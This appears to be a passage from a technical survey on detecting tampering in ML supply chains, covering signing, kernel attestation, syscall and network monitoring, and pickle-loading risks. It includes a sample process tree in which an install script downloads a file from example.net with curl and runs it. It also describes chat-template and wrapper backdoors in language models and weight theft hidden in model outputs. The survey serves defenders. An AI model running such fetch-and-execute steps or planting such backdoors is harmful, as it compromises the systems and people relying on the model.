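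Someone can also replace a file after it is verified but before it is loaded, as *Caleta* acknowledges. Kliukovkin describes two versions of this problem in KServe, a platform for serving models on clusters. KServe downloads the weights to a storage area that several containers may share, so another container could alter them after the check. If only the main container restarts, it loads the same copy again without a new check. Read-only storage reduces this risk. Sentry hashes the weights once they are in GPU memory, so swapping them on the disk before loading does not help an attacker. Linux also offers fs-verity, which makes a file read-only and checks each block against a Merkle tree whenever a program reads it from the disk.

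### Signing the whole model

A language model is usually a folder of files, and a signature over the weights alone would leave the others unprotected. *An Introduction to the OpenSSF Model Signing (OMS) Specification* (Maruseac, Wickens and colleagues, 2025) describes a format that covers all the files, which can include weights, configuration, tokenizers and datasets. (OpenSSF is the Open Source Security Foundation, an industry body.) The publisher lists every file in a manifest and signs the manifest once. Each entry contains the file's path and hash, according to Red Hat's *Model authenticity and transparency with Sigstore*. Sigstore's *Taming the Wild West of ML* introduces version 1.0 of a tool that creates or verifies such a signature with one command.

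A verifier must also look for files that the manifest does not list, for the same reason as with RECORD. IBM's *Signature verification* tells users of a signed Granite model to make sure that nobody has added, removed or modified files in their copy before they run the check.

A valid signature does not show that a model is current. An attacker who controls the storage can supply an older version with a known flaw, and its signature will still be valid. Kliukovkin's proposed check for KServe would therefore require the expected model name and, where possible, the version, as well as the right signer. KServe would also not start a model whose signature is missing, since anyone who can alter the weights can delete the signature file beside them. The same attacker could then stop the service by deleting signatures, a drawback that Kliukovkin accepts.

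### Why the weights are not enough

Several small files can change a model's behaviour while the weights stay the same. One is the tokenizer, which splits text into the units that the model processes. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) points out that an altered tokenizer can split dangerous strings differently. An adapter or a script in the model's folder can also change the model's answers.

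Chat templates have been tested most thoroughly. A chat template is a small program that runs on every request and arranges the conversation into the text format the model learned in training. Fogel, Cohen and colleagues (2026), in *Inference-Time Backdoors via Chat Templates*, added fewer than ten lines to these templates. If the user's latest message contained a trigger phrase, the altered template inserted hidden instructions at the start of the prompt. Otherwise it produced the same text as the original. Across eighteen models, the trigger reduced factual accuracy from 90% to 15% on average, and requests without the trigger showed no measurable loss. Hugging Face's automated scans did not detect the altered files.

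In GGUF, a common format for compressed models, the template sits in the same file as the weights. A hash of the whole file would detect a change to the template, which a hash of the weights alone would miss. But a whole-file hash is useful only if there is a trustworthy value to compare it with. Volunteers make many of the GGUF files in use by compressing weights that a developer released in another format, so the developer's hashes do not match these files. A user could instead extract the template, which compression need not alter, and compare it with the developer's copy.

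An attack can also be split across the files around a model. Arif, Lou and Zheng (2026), in *Conjunctive Poisoning in AI Supply-Chain Applications*, left their models unaltered and changed two other files: a settings file and the wrapper, a script that builds prompts and formats answers. The wrapper contained a hidden marker. The settings file contained a hash of that marker, computed with a secret key, and a hash of the wrapper. When the program ran, the wrapper recomputed both hashes and changed the model's answer only if both matched. A reviewer who examined only the settings file would see two strings with no apparent meaning, and one who examined only the wrapper would not know which values activated it.

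In the main test of five models, the changed output appeared in 91% to 100% of cases. The test used harmless changes, such as a banner above the answer. Scores on six of seven standard benchmarks moved by less than two percentage points, so a routine accuracy test would probably not have revealed the tampering. One of the five was a closed model that the wrapper called over the internet, so local wrapper files need monitoring even when the model runs elsewhere.

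When a signature covered the model but left out the wrapper and settings, the attack still succeeded in 75% to 82% of cases. The drop is hard to interpret because Arif and colleagues attribute success rates below 100% to the way programs displayed, parsed or filtered the answers, which a signature on the weights should not affect. They also argue that a signature over every file blocks the attack by construction. This follows from how signatures work, as long as the user accepts only the original publisher's signature. The demonstration is also limited because the secret key must be present where the wrapper runs, and a real attacker would need some way to put it there.

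Arif and colleagues propose hashing a simplified copy of the wrapper, without comments or extra spaces, so that tidying the file does not trigger an alarm. However, this also removes indentation, which in Python determines which lines belong to a condition. An attacker could therefore change what a script does without changing the simplified hash. A hash of the exact file would detect this change but cause more false alarms.

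### Modelstamp's tests

Modelstamp's record, which Dhekne described in September 2026, covers some of the software around a model as well as the model file. In full, it contains:

- the model file's name, size and SHA-256 hash, and the method that saved it
- the model's class and the module that defines it
- the Python version and implementation, the platform and the time of saving
- the installed versions of up to nine packages, and a list of those relevant to this model
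- optionally, the state of the project's source code and a keyed hash that authenticates the record

Ten of Dhekne's 14 tests of environment changes involved a relevant package. In one pair of tests, Modelstamp reported nothing when Dhekne changed six unrelated packages, and reported only scikit-learn when it was also updated from version 1.5.1 to 1.5.2. By default, Modelstamp only warns about a version difference and still loads the model, but if the hash is wrong, it stops loading before any code in the file can run.

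The nine packages belong to traditional machine learning and do not include PyTorch or Transformers, the libraries that most language models use. The package comparison would help little with the 70-billion-parameter model in the earlier example.

Dhekne also tested eight kinds of tampering. Modelstamp stopped four and accepted four, as its design predicts.

| Tampering | Result | Reason |
|---|---|---|
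| Alter the model file | Rejected | The hash no longer matches |
| Alter the hash in the record | Rejected | The file does not match the new hash |
| Replace a signed file and record with unsigned ones | Rejected | The user requires a signed record |
| Sign a replacement with an unknown key | Rejected | The user does not trust the key |
| Replace both the file and an unsigned record | Accepted | The new pair is consistent |
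| Alter the model's description in an unsigned record | Accepted | Nothing authenticates the description |
| Sign a replacement with the shared key | Accepted | Every holder of the key can sign |
| Restore an old signed file and record | Accepted | The old signature remains valid |

The accepted cases apply to most systems that keep a hash beside the file it describes. The user can prevent the first two by requiring a signed record. Preventing the third requires public-key signatures instead of a shared key. Preventing the last requires knowing from another source which version is current.

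### Protecting the record

An intruder with full control of a machine can alter the baseline, replace the monitor with a program that always reports success, and delete old reports. Administrators can keep the baseline on read-only media or another machine, but the reports need protection too.

The simplest measure is to send each report to another machine immediately. The intruder can stop new reports but cannot erase those already sent. If the monitor also sends a regular message when it has nothing to report, a missing message is a reason to investigate.

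A hash chain makes alterations to a log detectable. Each entry includes a hash of the entry before it, so if entry 50 is changed, it no longer matches the hash in entry 51. An intruder who can rewrite the whole log can recompute every hash from entry 50 onwards, making the chain consistent again. The chain therefore helps only if someone elsewhere holds a recent hash to compare. *Verifiable Manifest Signing and Transparency Enforcement for Secure MCP-Based LLM Pipelines* (2026) builds a similar log with a Merkle tree, and its guarantee also depends on exporting the tree's root hash. The tree makes audits faster, because an auditor needs only about 20 hashes to confirm that a particular entry is in a log of a million.

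These measures protect reports only after the monitor has written them. If the intruder already controls the monitor, the reports may be false from the start. Linux's Integrity Measurement Architecture (IMA) reduces this risk by moving the hashing into the kernel and part of the record into a security chip, the Trusted Platform Module (TPM). Before a program runs or reads a file that the policy covers, the kernel hashes the file, adds the hash to a list, and sends it to the chip. The chip has registers that software cannot set directly. Software can only update them by this rule:

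new register = H(old register ‖ new measurement)

H is a hash function such as SHA-256, and ‖ means joining two values end to end. The register starts at zero when the machine boots. For three files with measurements m1, m2 and m3, it takes these values:

- R1 = H(0 ‖ m1)
- R2 = H(R1 ‖ m2)
- R3 = H(R2 ‖ m3)

A toy hash, H, shows the effect. It joins a pair of two-digit numbers and takes the remainder after division by 97. Suppose the Python interpreter has measurement 12, the startup hook 34 and the training script 56.

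| File | Joined number | New register |
|---|---|---|
| Python interpreter | 0012 | 12 |
| Startup hook | 1234 | 70 |
| Training script | 7056 | 72 |

If the intruder then deletes the hook from the kernel's list, anyone who recomputes the register from the remaining two files gets 12 and then 92. The chip holds 72, so the list must be false. With this toy hash, the intruder could repair the mismatch by sending the chip a fourth measurement of 70, which changes the register from 72 to 92. With SHA-256, nobody knows a practical way to find such a value.

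Another machine can check the register through remote attestation:

1. The verifier sends a random number, so that the machine cannot reuse an old answer.
2. The chip signs the register values and the random number with a key that never leaves it.
3. The machine returns the signed values with the kernel's list.
4. The verifier recomputes the register from the list and compares it with the signed value.
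5. If they match, the verifier compares each hash on the list with the approved set.

The last step is essential because a correct list may still contain a malicious file. The fourth step uses the list because files load in a different order each time, and each order gives a different final value. In the toy example, loading the training script before the hook gives 19 instead of 72.

If the policy covers a file, the kernel records the file's measurement in the chip before running it. Malware that runs from such a file has therefore normally been recorded before it can take over the kernel. It can then prevent new measurements, but it cannot remove its own without restarting the machine. The verifier must also confirm that the machine started with an approved kernel. On a suitably configured machine, the firmware and boot loader use other registers to record which kernel was loaded.

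IMA's coverage depends on its policy. A commonly used policy measures programs, shared libraries, kernel modules and files that the administrator account reads. It would measure the Python interpreter, but not a startup hook that Python reads under a researcher's ordinary account. Extending the policy to every file that the training account reads would cover the hook, but the kernel would then have to hash all 140 GB of weights before the job could open them. fs-verity suits the weights better because it checks blocks as the job reads them.

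### What file monitoring misses

File monitoring can't detect malware that was already present when the baseline was made. If the team in the earlier example made its baseline after the researcher installed the plotting package, every later scan would report the startup hook as unchanged. Dhekne describes the same limitation in Modelstamp, where a model that was malicious when someone first saved it passes every check. Malware can also enter the baseline if an administrator accepts a long list of differences after an upgrade without reading it. It is safer to build the baseline from a fresh installation of the lockfile on a clean machine than from a machine already in use.

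The second-stage script in the example runs only in memory, so there is no file to hash. IMA does not measure it either, because its activity appears to the kernel only as a network connection and ordinary memory use. Some malware instead writes its code to a directory that Linux keeps in memory, such as /dev/shm. Although inotify reports changes to files there, the files disappear when the machine restarts, and many scan policies exclude the directory.

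File monitoring cannot detect the replaced grader either, since even the settings file that names it keeps the same hash.

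## What does monitoring processes and system calls add?

The second-stage script in the earlier example is never saved as a file, but it still has to read the team's access keys and send them out. On Linux, both steps require system calls, which are requests to the operating system's kernel to open a file, start a process or make a connection. A monitor that records system calls can therefore collect evidence of a memory-only change while it happens.

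### The Linux audit system

Linux has a built-in recorder called the audit system. An administrator loads rules into the kernel, for example to record every program start or every attempt to open a file containing keys. When a process makes a system call, the kernel saves the arguments on entry. On exit, it adds the result and writes a record if a rule matches.

The record of a program start includes:

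- the time and a serial number
- the number of the process and of its parent, the process that started it
- the program's path and arguments
- the user account, and the account under which the person first logged in
- whether the call succeeded

A record of a file access adds the file's path, and a record of a connection adds the remote address.

The kernel places these records in a queue, and a separate program, auditd, moves them to a log on disk. *Ellipsis* (2022) explains that the kernel and auditd work independently, so the queue can overflow, as inotify's can. Suppose the queue holds 8,192 records, the kernel adds 50,000 a second and auditd removes 30,000. The queue then grows by 20,000 records a second and fills in about 0.4 seconds, after which the kernel loses 40% of new records. The kernel counts the losses, so an administrator can tell that the log is incomplete, but not what is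 missing.

Houssel, Levillain and colleagues (2026), in *A Study of Kernel Telemetry Options for Security-Oriented Provenance*, measured such losses by making 50,000 connections, writing 50,000 files or starting 50,000 processes, then counting how many of these events a tool recorded. SPADE, a research system that relies on auditd, lost between 91% and 99% of the events. Most machines are less busy than this, but a large package installation can produce a similar burst just when the records matter most.

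### eBPF monitors

Newer monitors use eBPF, a Linux facility for running small programs inside the kernel. Before loading a program, the kernel checks that it will finish and will not corrupt memory. Falco, Tracee and Tetragon, three widely used open-source security monitors, can all use eBPF. They attach their eBPF programs to hooks, which are points in the kernel's code where extra programs can run.

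| Hook | Location | Main advantage or drawback |
|---|---|---|
| Tracepoint | Fixed markers in the kernel, including the entry and exit of system calls | Changes little between kernel versions |
| Kprobe | The start or end of almost any kernel function | Covers more, but a kernel update can break it |
| LSM hook | The point where the kernel consults its security modules about an operation | Can record only operations that the kernel allowed |

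A hook at the entry of a system call also records attempts that the kernel then refuses. A refused attempt to read a key file deserves an alert, but an investigator deciding which keys to replace needs to know which attempts succeeded. The monitor must therefore also record the call's result on exit, or use an LSM hook that runs after the other security checks.

The eBPF program copies the details of each event into a ring buffer, an area of memory that the monitor's main process reads. In the tests by Houssel and colleagues, each event contained the process ID, user, program name and container ID. The container ID makes it possible to tell one team's job from the others on a shared server.

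New events can also be lost when a ring buffer is full, as *Diagnosing applications' I/O behavior through system call observability* (2023) describes. In the paper's tests, the eBPF tracer Sysdig could not give a file path for 45% of events. An event without a path cannot trigger a rule about a particular key file, so an event count alone overstates how much a monitor has captured.

Heavy event loss is avoidable. The research tool eAudit recorded 81 kinds of system call and lost no events in any of the three workloads that Houssel and colleagues ran. The four systems that connected events into a graph during the test lost 90% or more of events in most workloads. eAudit leaves that step until later. It also gives each processor its own buffer, stores events compactly and prioritises some system calls.

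### What monitoring costs

Houssel and colleagues measured the processor time of each workload on a 24-core server, with and without a simple eBPF program that recorded one type of event. Recording events at system call entry added 0.8% to 1.7% for network connections, 1.2% to 1.3% for process starts, and 8.1% to 9.1% for file creation. A full monitor adds more overhead; eAudit added 5.9% for the network workload and 12% for the file workload.

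Limiting the monitor to one container reduces its overhead. When two containers started processes and only one was of interest, an eBPF program attached to that container added 0.45%, compared with 1.66% for recording both and discarding the unwanted events afterwards.

Older tracers such as strace slow a program much more because they interrupt it at every system call. In *Diagnosing applications' I/O behavior through system call observability*, a workload took 1.71 times as long with strace and 1.04 times as long with Sysdig. Sysdig missed many file paths in that test, so part of its advantage may come from recording less.

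All these workloads use the kernel unusually heavily. *Auditing Frameworks Need Resource Isolation* (2023) found that programs limited by the processor, such as compression software, make almost no system calls. Monitoring would probably slow a training job only a little during its matrix arithmetic, and more while the job reads a dataset of many small files. A busy process elsewhere on the machine can also slow the job, because the monitor takes processor time from the job to handle that process's events.

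### A package installation as a process tree

A single event often means little. A developer may use the download program curl many times a day. What started curl is more informative, and the monitor can work this out because each process record includes the parent's number. The result is a tree, such as this one for a malicious package that pip builds from source:

```
pip install examplepkg
└─ python3 setup.py
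   ├─ gcc module.c
   └─ sh
      ├─ curl https://example.net/tool
      └─ /tmp/tool
```

The compiler, gcc, is normal for a package with parts written in C. The shell, sh, is normal too, since build scripts often use one and npm runs install scripts through one. The start of curl separates this tree from a normal installation. Normally the installer itself downloads packages from the registry, but here a process three levels below pip fetches a file from another address. The shell then runs that file, which is stronger evidence than the download alone.

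Some legitimate packages also download a compiled program during installation, so an alert on every such download would produce false alarms. Datadog Security Labs' *A runtime security approach to detecting supply chain attacks* (2025) describes a rule that requires more evidence. When somebody runs an npm install command, the monitor gives that process a random label, which every process descended from it inherits. Other rules assign suspicious events to attack tactics, such as searching for credentials or sending data out. If events with the same label cover more than two tactics, the system raises a serious alert.

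Datadog Security Labs tried the rule on a simulation of Shai-Hulud, a self-spreading npm attack that compromised more than 500 packages in September 2025. The malware ran TruffleHog, a legitimate program for finding leaked passwords and keys. A security team may run it every week, but there is no obvious reason for an npm installation to do so. The rule would also cover the TanStack attack described earlier, because the optional dependency's script still ran below the install command. The company, which sells the monitor, gives no detection or false-alarm rate, so the simulation shows only that the rule can work.

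### The memory-only script

The rule for installations would miss the second-stage script in the earlier example, because the plotting package's dependency only places a startup hook on disk. The hook runs the next time Python starts, when the parent process is probably a notebook or a training job rather than pip. To catch the script, the team would need a second label that begins with the job.

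| Step | What the monitor can record |
|---|---|
| Python reads the startup hook | A .pth file opened |
| The hook downloads the script | A connection from Python to an unfamiliar address |
| Python runs the script | No distinctive system call |
| The script reads the keys | The key file opened |
| The script sends the keys | A connection or outgoing data |

Python runs the script inside the existing process, so monitoring does not show a new program starting. The useful evidence is that one process opens an unfamiliar connection, reads the key file and sends more data, all within a few seconds. A rule listing the programs allowed to open the key file would raise an alert earlier, provided the training job does not need the file itself.

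Many teams pass keys to a job as environment variables instead. These are already in the process's memory when it starts, so the script can read them without a system call, and the only evidence is the connections. In either case, the records do not contain the script's code. The team can use them to work out when the theft probably happened and which process was involved, and the hook left on disk may show where the script came from.

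### Tests on Python packages

In *QUT-DV25*, Mehedi, Jurdak and colleagues (2025) report the largest of these tests on Python packages. They ran 14,271 packages, 7,127 of them malicious, on 16 Raspberry Pi computers and recorded their behaviour with eBPF. They counted a package as malicious if at least two of three security services did, and as benign only if all three agreed. They inspected the unclear cases by hand.

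Each package had a fresh Python environment. The researchers recorded its installation and the following 120 seconds, having found no new behaviour after that point in a trial of 64 high-risk packages. They reduced the recordings to 36 features, covering file activity, directories opened, network connections, system calls, dependencies and common sequences of calls. They then trained several models to separate malicious packages from benign ones. For comparison, they also trained models on the packages' source code and on metadata such as descriptions and authors. The results for a random forest, a model that combines many decision trees, were:

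| Information used | Malicious packages detected | Benign packages flagged |
|---|---|---|
| Metadata | 82.98% | 13.90% |
| Source code | 93.37% | 2.94% |
| Recorded behaviour | 95.26% | 3.23% |

(The paper's text gives 96.36% and 1.74% for the behavioural model, but its own table attributes these figures to two other models.)

Behaviour was much more informative than metadata but only slightly more informative than source code. With another type of model, a support vector machine, detection was 96.36% from behaviour and 96.01% from source code. *DySec* (2025), which describes a detector for the same packages, reports 78.65% fewer missed attacks than static analysis. The random forest figures above imply a reduction of only about 29%, so the benefit depends heavily on which static detector is used for comparison. A stronger reason to record behaviour is to detect attacks whose code is not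 in the package, such as the second-stage script.

Sequences of system calls alone gave 94.62% accuracy, compared with 83.74% for network connections and 69.45% for the list of installed dependencies. This suggests that much of the information is in the order of events, as it is in the process tree.

Half the packages in the dataset are malicious, a far higher share than on PyPI, where Mehedi and colleagues put it at 1.2% in July 2024. At that rate, the random forest would detect about 114 of the 120 malicious packages in a set of 10,000 and flag about 319 benign ones, so roughly one alarm in four would be real. If only one package in 1,000 were malicious, which may still be too high for a team that mostly installs popular software, about 3% of alarms would be real.

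The researchers also tried the model on 1,000 recent PyPI packages that had been considered benign. It flagged 11, and they judged six to be malicious. PyPI removed four but kept the other two, which have both legitimate and harmful uses. One was PySocks, which sends network traffic through an intermediary. The false-alarm rate was 0.5% if those two count as malicious and 0.7% if they don't, well below the rate in the main test. The researchers followed up only on flagged packages, so this test doesn't show how many attacks the model missed.

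The test conditions leave out attacks that wait more than two minutes, need a user's action or particular arguments, or run only on Windows or macOS. A Raspberry Pi also lacks the GPUs and cloud credentials of a training server, so malware that looks for either might do nothing. The results apply to a package running alone on a clean machine, which is an easier setting than a server running many other programs.

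The Open Source Security Foundation's package-analysis project uses a similar method to examine packages from several registries, including PyPI and npm. *Pack-A-Mal* (2025) describes how the project places each package in a container inside another container, then installs, imports and executes it. The project uses the system calls to identify network connections, files accessed and commands run. Importing the package matters because it can do nothing suspicious during installation and act only when a program first uses it.

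These recordings still need interpretation. *Towards Measuring Supply Chain Attacks on Package Managers for Interpreted Languages* (2020) used simple rules, such as flagging a package that contacts anything other than a registry or code host, or that opens sensitive files. The researchers then had to check the flagged packages by hand.

### Why loading a model can run code

Pickle, the PyTorch format mentioned earlier, can run code during loading because it stores instructions for rebuilding Python objects. One instruction can name a function for Python to import, and another can call it with arguments from the file. A legitimate model file uses these instructions to recreate its weight arrays, but the format does not limit which functions a file may call.

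*PickleBall* (Kellas, Li and colleagues, 2025) found pickle files in 44.9% of Hugging Face repositories with at least 1,000 downloads a month. Safer formats exist, including SafeTensors, which stores only the weights. PyTorch also has a restricted loader, on by default since version 2.6, that permits only a short list of functions. The loader could not load at least one model in 15.4% of the pickle-only repositories sampled, and some libraries turn it off for this reason.

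PickleBall analyses each library's source code to list the functions its models need, then blocks all others during loading. In a test on 84 malicious and 252 benign models, it stopped every malicious one but also rejected 51 benign ones, a false-positive rate of 20.2%. The errors were concentrated in a few libraries. PickleBall loaded all 76 models from sentence_transformers, a text library, but only 19 of 63 from two versions of the image-recognition library YOLO.

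The same test included ModelTracer, which runs a model and watches for a few suspicious operations, such as starting a program or opening a connection. It flagged no benign models but missed 40 of the 84 malicious ones, partly because it did not monitor file access. Tracing system calls therefore works poorly if the list of suspicious calls is too short.

### RE-MOAT

RE-MOAT lists what a model is expected to do and flags everything else, which is the reverse of ModelTracer's approach. Digregorio, Di Gennaro and colleagues (2026), in *Lifecycle-Aware Dynamic Analysis for Secure ML Model Execution*, argue that this is practical for models but not for software in general. PyTorch models mostly run the same PyTorch code on different numbers, whereas two text editors may use the operating system in quite different ways.

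The expected actions depend on the framework and on what it is doing:

| Phase | Examples of expected actions | Tested with |
|---|---|---|
| Loading | Read the model's folder and Python's own files, write to PyTorch's temporary loading paths, print messages | PyTorch, Keras |
| Inference (producing answers) | For TensorFlow, read the model, system libraries and processor information, and run a program that identifies the system | PyTorch, Keras, TensorFlow |
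| Training | No list in the implementation | Not tested |

To make the lists, the researchers recorded the actions of 600 benign models they had generated and about 1,000 from Hugging Face. They checked by hand whether an untrusted model could abuse each new action. Each list has between 4 and 21 entries. A list might allow reads from the model's folder but not from the folder that holds a user's login keys.

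RE-MOAT starts the framework and loads its libraries first, so that their routine activity does not count against the model. It then marks the beginning and end of the phase and compares every system call in between with the list. It uses the same slow mechanism as strace, which added at most about three seconds on average when Digregorio and colleagues measured it. They consider this acceptable for scanning a model before use, but recommend a faster method such as eBPF for continuous monitoring.

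They ran three tests:

1. **31 proof-of-concept attacks.** These used eight published vulnerabilities, one that was not yet public, and an earlier method of abusing TensorFlow's normal functions. Their aims included stealing a file and gaining remote access. RE-MOAT detected all 31, although the researchers had fixed the lists before they built the attacks.
2. **77,974 public model files.** The researchers collected 88,789 PyTorch and Keras files from Hugging Face and excluded those that needed additional software. They tested only loading. RE-MOAT flagged 23 files, and a manual check confirmed that all 23 were malicious.
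3. **334 comparison models.** These came from PickleBall's dataset, after the removal of three attacks that work only on Windows. RE-MOAT made no errors under the researchers' own definition of a malicious model.

The second test is strong evidence of a low false-alarm rate. It produced no false alarms among roughly 78,000 files, which puts the usual 95% upper limit for similar files at about 3 / 78,000, or one in 26,000. It is much weaker evidence about missed attacks, because the researchers checked only the files that RE-MOAT flagged. The third test does measure misses and found none, but it included only 59 models that were malicious under the researchers' definition, so the true miss rate could still be about 5%.

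The number of errors also depends on how "malicious" is defined. Digregorio and colleagues relabelled 21 models from malicious to benign because the models did no harm to the machine. Eighteen of these only printed a message or did something similar. The table gives error counts under both sets of labels.

| Tool | Benign models rejected, new labels (of 275) | Malicious models missed, new labels (of 59) | Benign models rejected, earlier labels (of 254) | Malicious models missed, earlier labels (of 80) |
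|---|---|---|---|---|
| RE-MOAT | 0 | 0 | 0 | 21 |
| PickleBall | 73 | 0 | 52 | 0 |
| ModelScan | 35 | 5 | 16 | 7 |
| ModelTracer | 1 | 17 | 1 | 38 |
| PyTorch's restricted loader | 117 | 0 | 96 | 0 |

(ModelScan searches a model file for known dangerous functions without running it.)

Under the earlier labels, RE-MOAT missed 26.2% of malicious models, while PickleBall missed none and wrongly rejected 20.5% of benign ones. The new labels are reasonable if the aim is to prevent damage, but the earlier ones are arguably better for detecting unauthorised changes, which need not be harmful. For example, a model that unexpectedly runs code to print a message differs from what a team would think it had approved.

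PickleBall blocks a forbidden function before it runs, whereas RE-MOAT, as built, lets the model run and logs the violation. RE-MOAT therefore needs an isolated machine, but it can check formats other than pickle and detect attacks that begin only during inference. A team could use both tools, or avoid much of the problem by accepting only SafeTensors files.

Extending the method to training would probably be harder. The job in the earlier example has to write checkpoints, start worker processes and send sample outputs to a grader on another company's server. Its list would have to allow network connections and file changes, which are among the clearest signs of an attack during loading. The list could specify exact addresses and directories, but someone would then have to update it whenever the job changed.

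RE-MOAT does not cover backdoors that alter only a model's answers. Changing the weights changes the numbers in the matrix arithmetic, which makes no system calls, so the altered model can read the same files and start the same processes as the original. The altered chat templates described earlier also insert hidden instructions into the prompt without requiring new system calls. Finding such changes requires comparing the files with a trusted hash or testing the model's answers.

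### The limits of system call records

System calls show what a program does but not why. A backup program and a credential stealer may both open a key file and then send data over the network. The process tree and the network destination help distinguish them, but sometimes only the machine's owner knows whether the action was intended.

The records also give little detail about what happens inside a program. When Python imports a module, the kernel receives requests to open and read a file, much as it does when Python reads a dataset. A rule can match files ending in .py or .pyc, but the records do not show which functions ran afterwards. Python can report imports through its own audit events, which a team could combine with the system call records.

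A monitor may also miss some kernel operations, and an attacker with full privileges may be able to disable it. As with file monitoring, immediately sending events to another machine protects those already recorded. *Rethinking Tamper-Evident Logging* (2025) presents NITRO, which uses eBPF to make later changes to the log detectable.

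## What can network monitoring detect?

An intruder who controls a machine may be able to switch off the monitors running on it, but a sensor elsewhere on the network keeps recording. It can log software downloads and outgoing traffic (egress). Most of this traffic is now encrypted, so the logs often contain only server names, times and sizes. The logs are most useful for machines that normally contact a few known destinations.

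### One installation through five sensors

Suppose the researcher in the earlier example installs version 3.1 of the plotting package from PyPI. pip looks up the network address of pypi.org, opens an encrypted connection and requests the package's index page, which lists the available files. It then downloads a file from a second host, files.pythonhosted.org, and repeats these requests for each dependency.

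Many organisations route such requests through a registry proxy, an internal server that fetches packages from public registries, keeps copies and passes them on. The first row of the table applies when pip uses a proxy, and the other rows apply when it contacts PyPI directly.

| Sensor | What it records | What it misses |
|---|---|---|
| Registry proxy | The time, the machine or account, and the name, version and hash of the plotting package and each dependency | Downloads that bypass the proxy, and anything a package does after installation |
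| Domain-name lookups | The time, the machine, the two host names and the addresses returned | The package, its version, and whether a download followed |
| Connection records | The address and port at each end, the start time, the duration and the bytes sent each way | The package and, usually, the host's name |
| Server name in the encrypted handshake | The two host names, each tied to a particular connection | The package and its version |
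| Full inspection of decrypted traffic | The complete web address of each file, which includes the package's name and version, and the file itself | The meaning of anything a program encrypted separately before sending it |

Only the proxy and full inspection identify the package. The proxy's log can be the observed set O for downloads, and a program can compare it with the approved set A before the proxy answers a request. This check would report both the plotting package and the dependency that contains the startup hook, and could block them. Some proxies can also delay new releases for a few days.

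The log also helps after an attack. A team that heard about the two malicious agent-framework releases could search the log for them and find every machine that had downloaded them through the proxy. The team would also need to delete the proxy's own copies, because a proxy can keep supplying a release after PyPI has removed it.

The server name is visible because the client sends it before encryption begins. The name identifies which site the client is requesting, since one network address often serves many websites. Malware can send a false name, and a newer protocol extension called Encrypted Client Hello hides the name.

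Fully inspecting encrypted traffic requires a proxy that decrypts the traffic, examines it and encrypts it again. The machines must trust the proxy's certificate, and programs that accept only the original server's certificate stop working. The proxy also decrypts every password and key in the traffic, which makes it an attractive target for attackers.

### The three changes in the example

| Sensor | Startup hook | Second-stage script | Replaced grader |
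|---|---|---|---|
| Registry proxy | The dependency that contained the hook | Nothing | Nothing |
| Domain-name lookups | The registry's usual names | An unfamiliar name, if the hook uses one | The usual name |
| Connection records | Ordinary downloads | An unfamiliar address and a small upload | The usual address, perhaps with slightly different volumes |
| Server name | The registry's usual names | An unfamiliar name, unless it is false or hidden | The usual name |
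| Full inspection | The package file with the hook inside | The script and the stolen keys, unless separately encrypted | The text of the old and new answers |

Full inspection can capture the second-stage script's code, which neither file scans nor system call records preserve. But the team would have to store the contents of downloads, and many organisations keep only a summary. No sensor identifies the replaced grader, although the team could compare any stored answers.

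### Traces of simulated attacks

In *An Empirical Study of Observability Limits in Advanced Software Supply Chain Attacks*, Tan, Brierley and colleagues (2026) recorded seven simulated attacks amid ordinary activity. They monitored three of the attacks with Zeek, an open-source program that turns network traffic into logs. The table shows how many Zeek records contained a known sign of the attack, such as the attacker's address.

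| Attack | Connections | Name lookups | Unencrypted web requests | Encrypted handshakes | Files transferred |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| npm package that ran parallel scripts | 96 | 6 | 4 | 0 | 0 |
| Chain of npm packages | 6 | 4 | 0 | 3 | 0 |
| Tampered AI model | 155 | 4 | 77 | 0 | 77 |

The chain of npm packages used encryption and left only 13 Zeek records among 188,270 records of all kinds. The handshake log helped in this case because the attacker's server used a self-signed certificate, which is unusual for a public website. An attacker could remove that clue by getting a free certificate from a recognised authority.

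These counts show that evidence existed, but a defender would not have known which addresses to look for. When Tan and colleagues used general rules instead, Zeek alone recovered 27% of the expected attack steps in the three scenarios.

### Allowlists and learned baselines

An egress allowlist names the permitted destinations, and a firewall or proxy blocks all others. The training job in the example might need only the registry proxy, a storage service and the grader. The hook's attempt to download the second-stage script would then fail, and the blocked connection would alert the team.

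Such a list is harder to write for build pipelines, which use many outside tools. GitHub (2024) let customers place its build machines, called runners, on a private network with outbound rules. In its security roadmap, GitHub (2026) still described unrestricted network access as a way for credentials to leak, and promised network limits that customers could enforce. Robert writes in *GitHub Actions 2026 security roadmap* that the planned firewall starts in an observation mode. Customers can then write rules for domains or address ranges and enforce them gradually. Canadian Web Hosting's *GitHub Actions 2026 Security Roadmap* puts the public preview six to nine months away and gives no date for general release.

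A monitor can also create the list by recording every destination contacted during a number of ordinary builds. It then reports any new one. This suits build machines because they repeat the same work, but a new dependency or a relocated download also produces a new destination. If an organisation runs 10,000 builds a day and 0.2% of them contact somewhere new for an innocent reason, the monitor raises 20 false alarms a day. As with a file baseline, if recording begins after the startup hook is installed, the monitor may treat the attack's connections as normal.

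Network access alone is weak evidence that a package is malicious, because many benign packages also make connections, as *Towards Robust Detection of Open Source Software Supply Chain Poisoning Attacks* (2024) points out. Mehedi and colleagues trained a model on connection data alone. If its error rate were the same for malicious and benign packages, only about 6% of the packages it flagged would be malicious, given PyPI's rate of malicious packages. An allowlist for one job should do better, because it can be tailored to the connections that job needs.

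It is uncertain how much more blocking unapproved connections helps, because the public claims come mainly from vendors. Kurmi (2026) writes for StepSecurity, which sells a tool that blocks such connections from runners. The article cites the Megalodon campaign, which took secrets from 5,500 public repositories, and GhostAction, which stole more than 3,000 secrets, as attacks that depended on outbound connections. This is a plausible argument for blocking, but it does not measure how many attacks an allowlist stops or how many legitimate builds it breaks. There seem to be no independent figures for either.

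### Limits on outbound volume

A limit on outbound volume can slow the theft of model weights even if the attacker uses a permitted destination. If the team's machines can together send at most 1 MB per second, the 140 GB of weights in the example would take about 39 hours to send. A 4 kB file of access keys would take 0.004 seconds, so the limit would not protect against the theft in the example.

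Compression makes the limit less effective for weights too. Brown, Rivera and colleagues (2026), in *Aggressive Compression Enables LLM Weight Theft*, consider an attacker who controls a server that answers customers' questions, and who hides pieces of the model in the answers sent to fake accounts. In their model, the theft takes

T = C / (E × N × s) days.

C is the compressed size of the model in bits, E is the number of bits sent to each user per day, N is the number of fake accounts, and s is the fraction of the output that can carry hidden data. If the defender has a fixed probability p of noticing the attack each day, an attack lasting T days succeeds with probability (1 − p)^T. When p is 1%, a 160-day attack succeeds about 20% of the time. Compressing the model to one-sixteenth of its size shortens the attack to 10 days and raises the success rate to about 90%.

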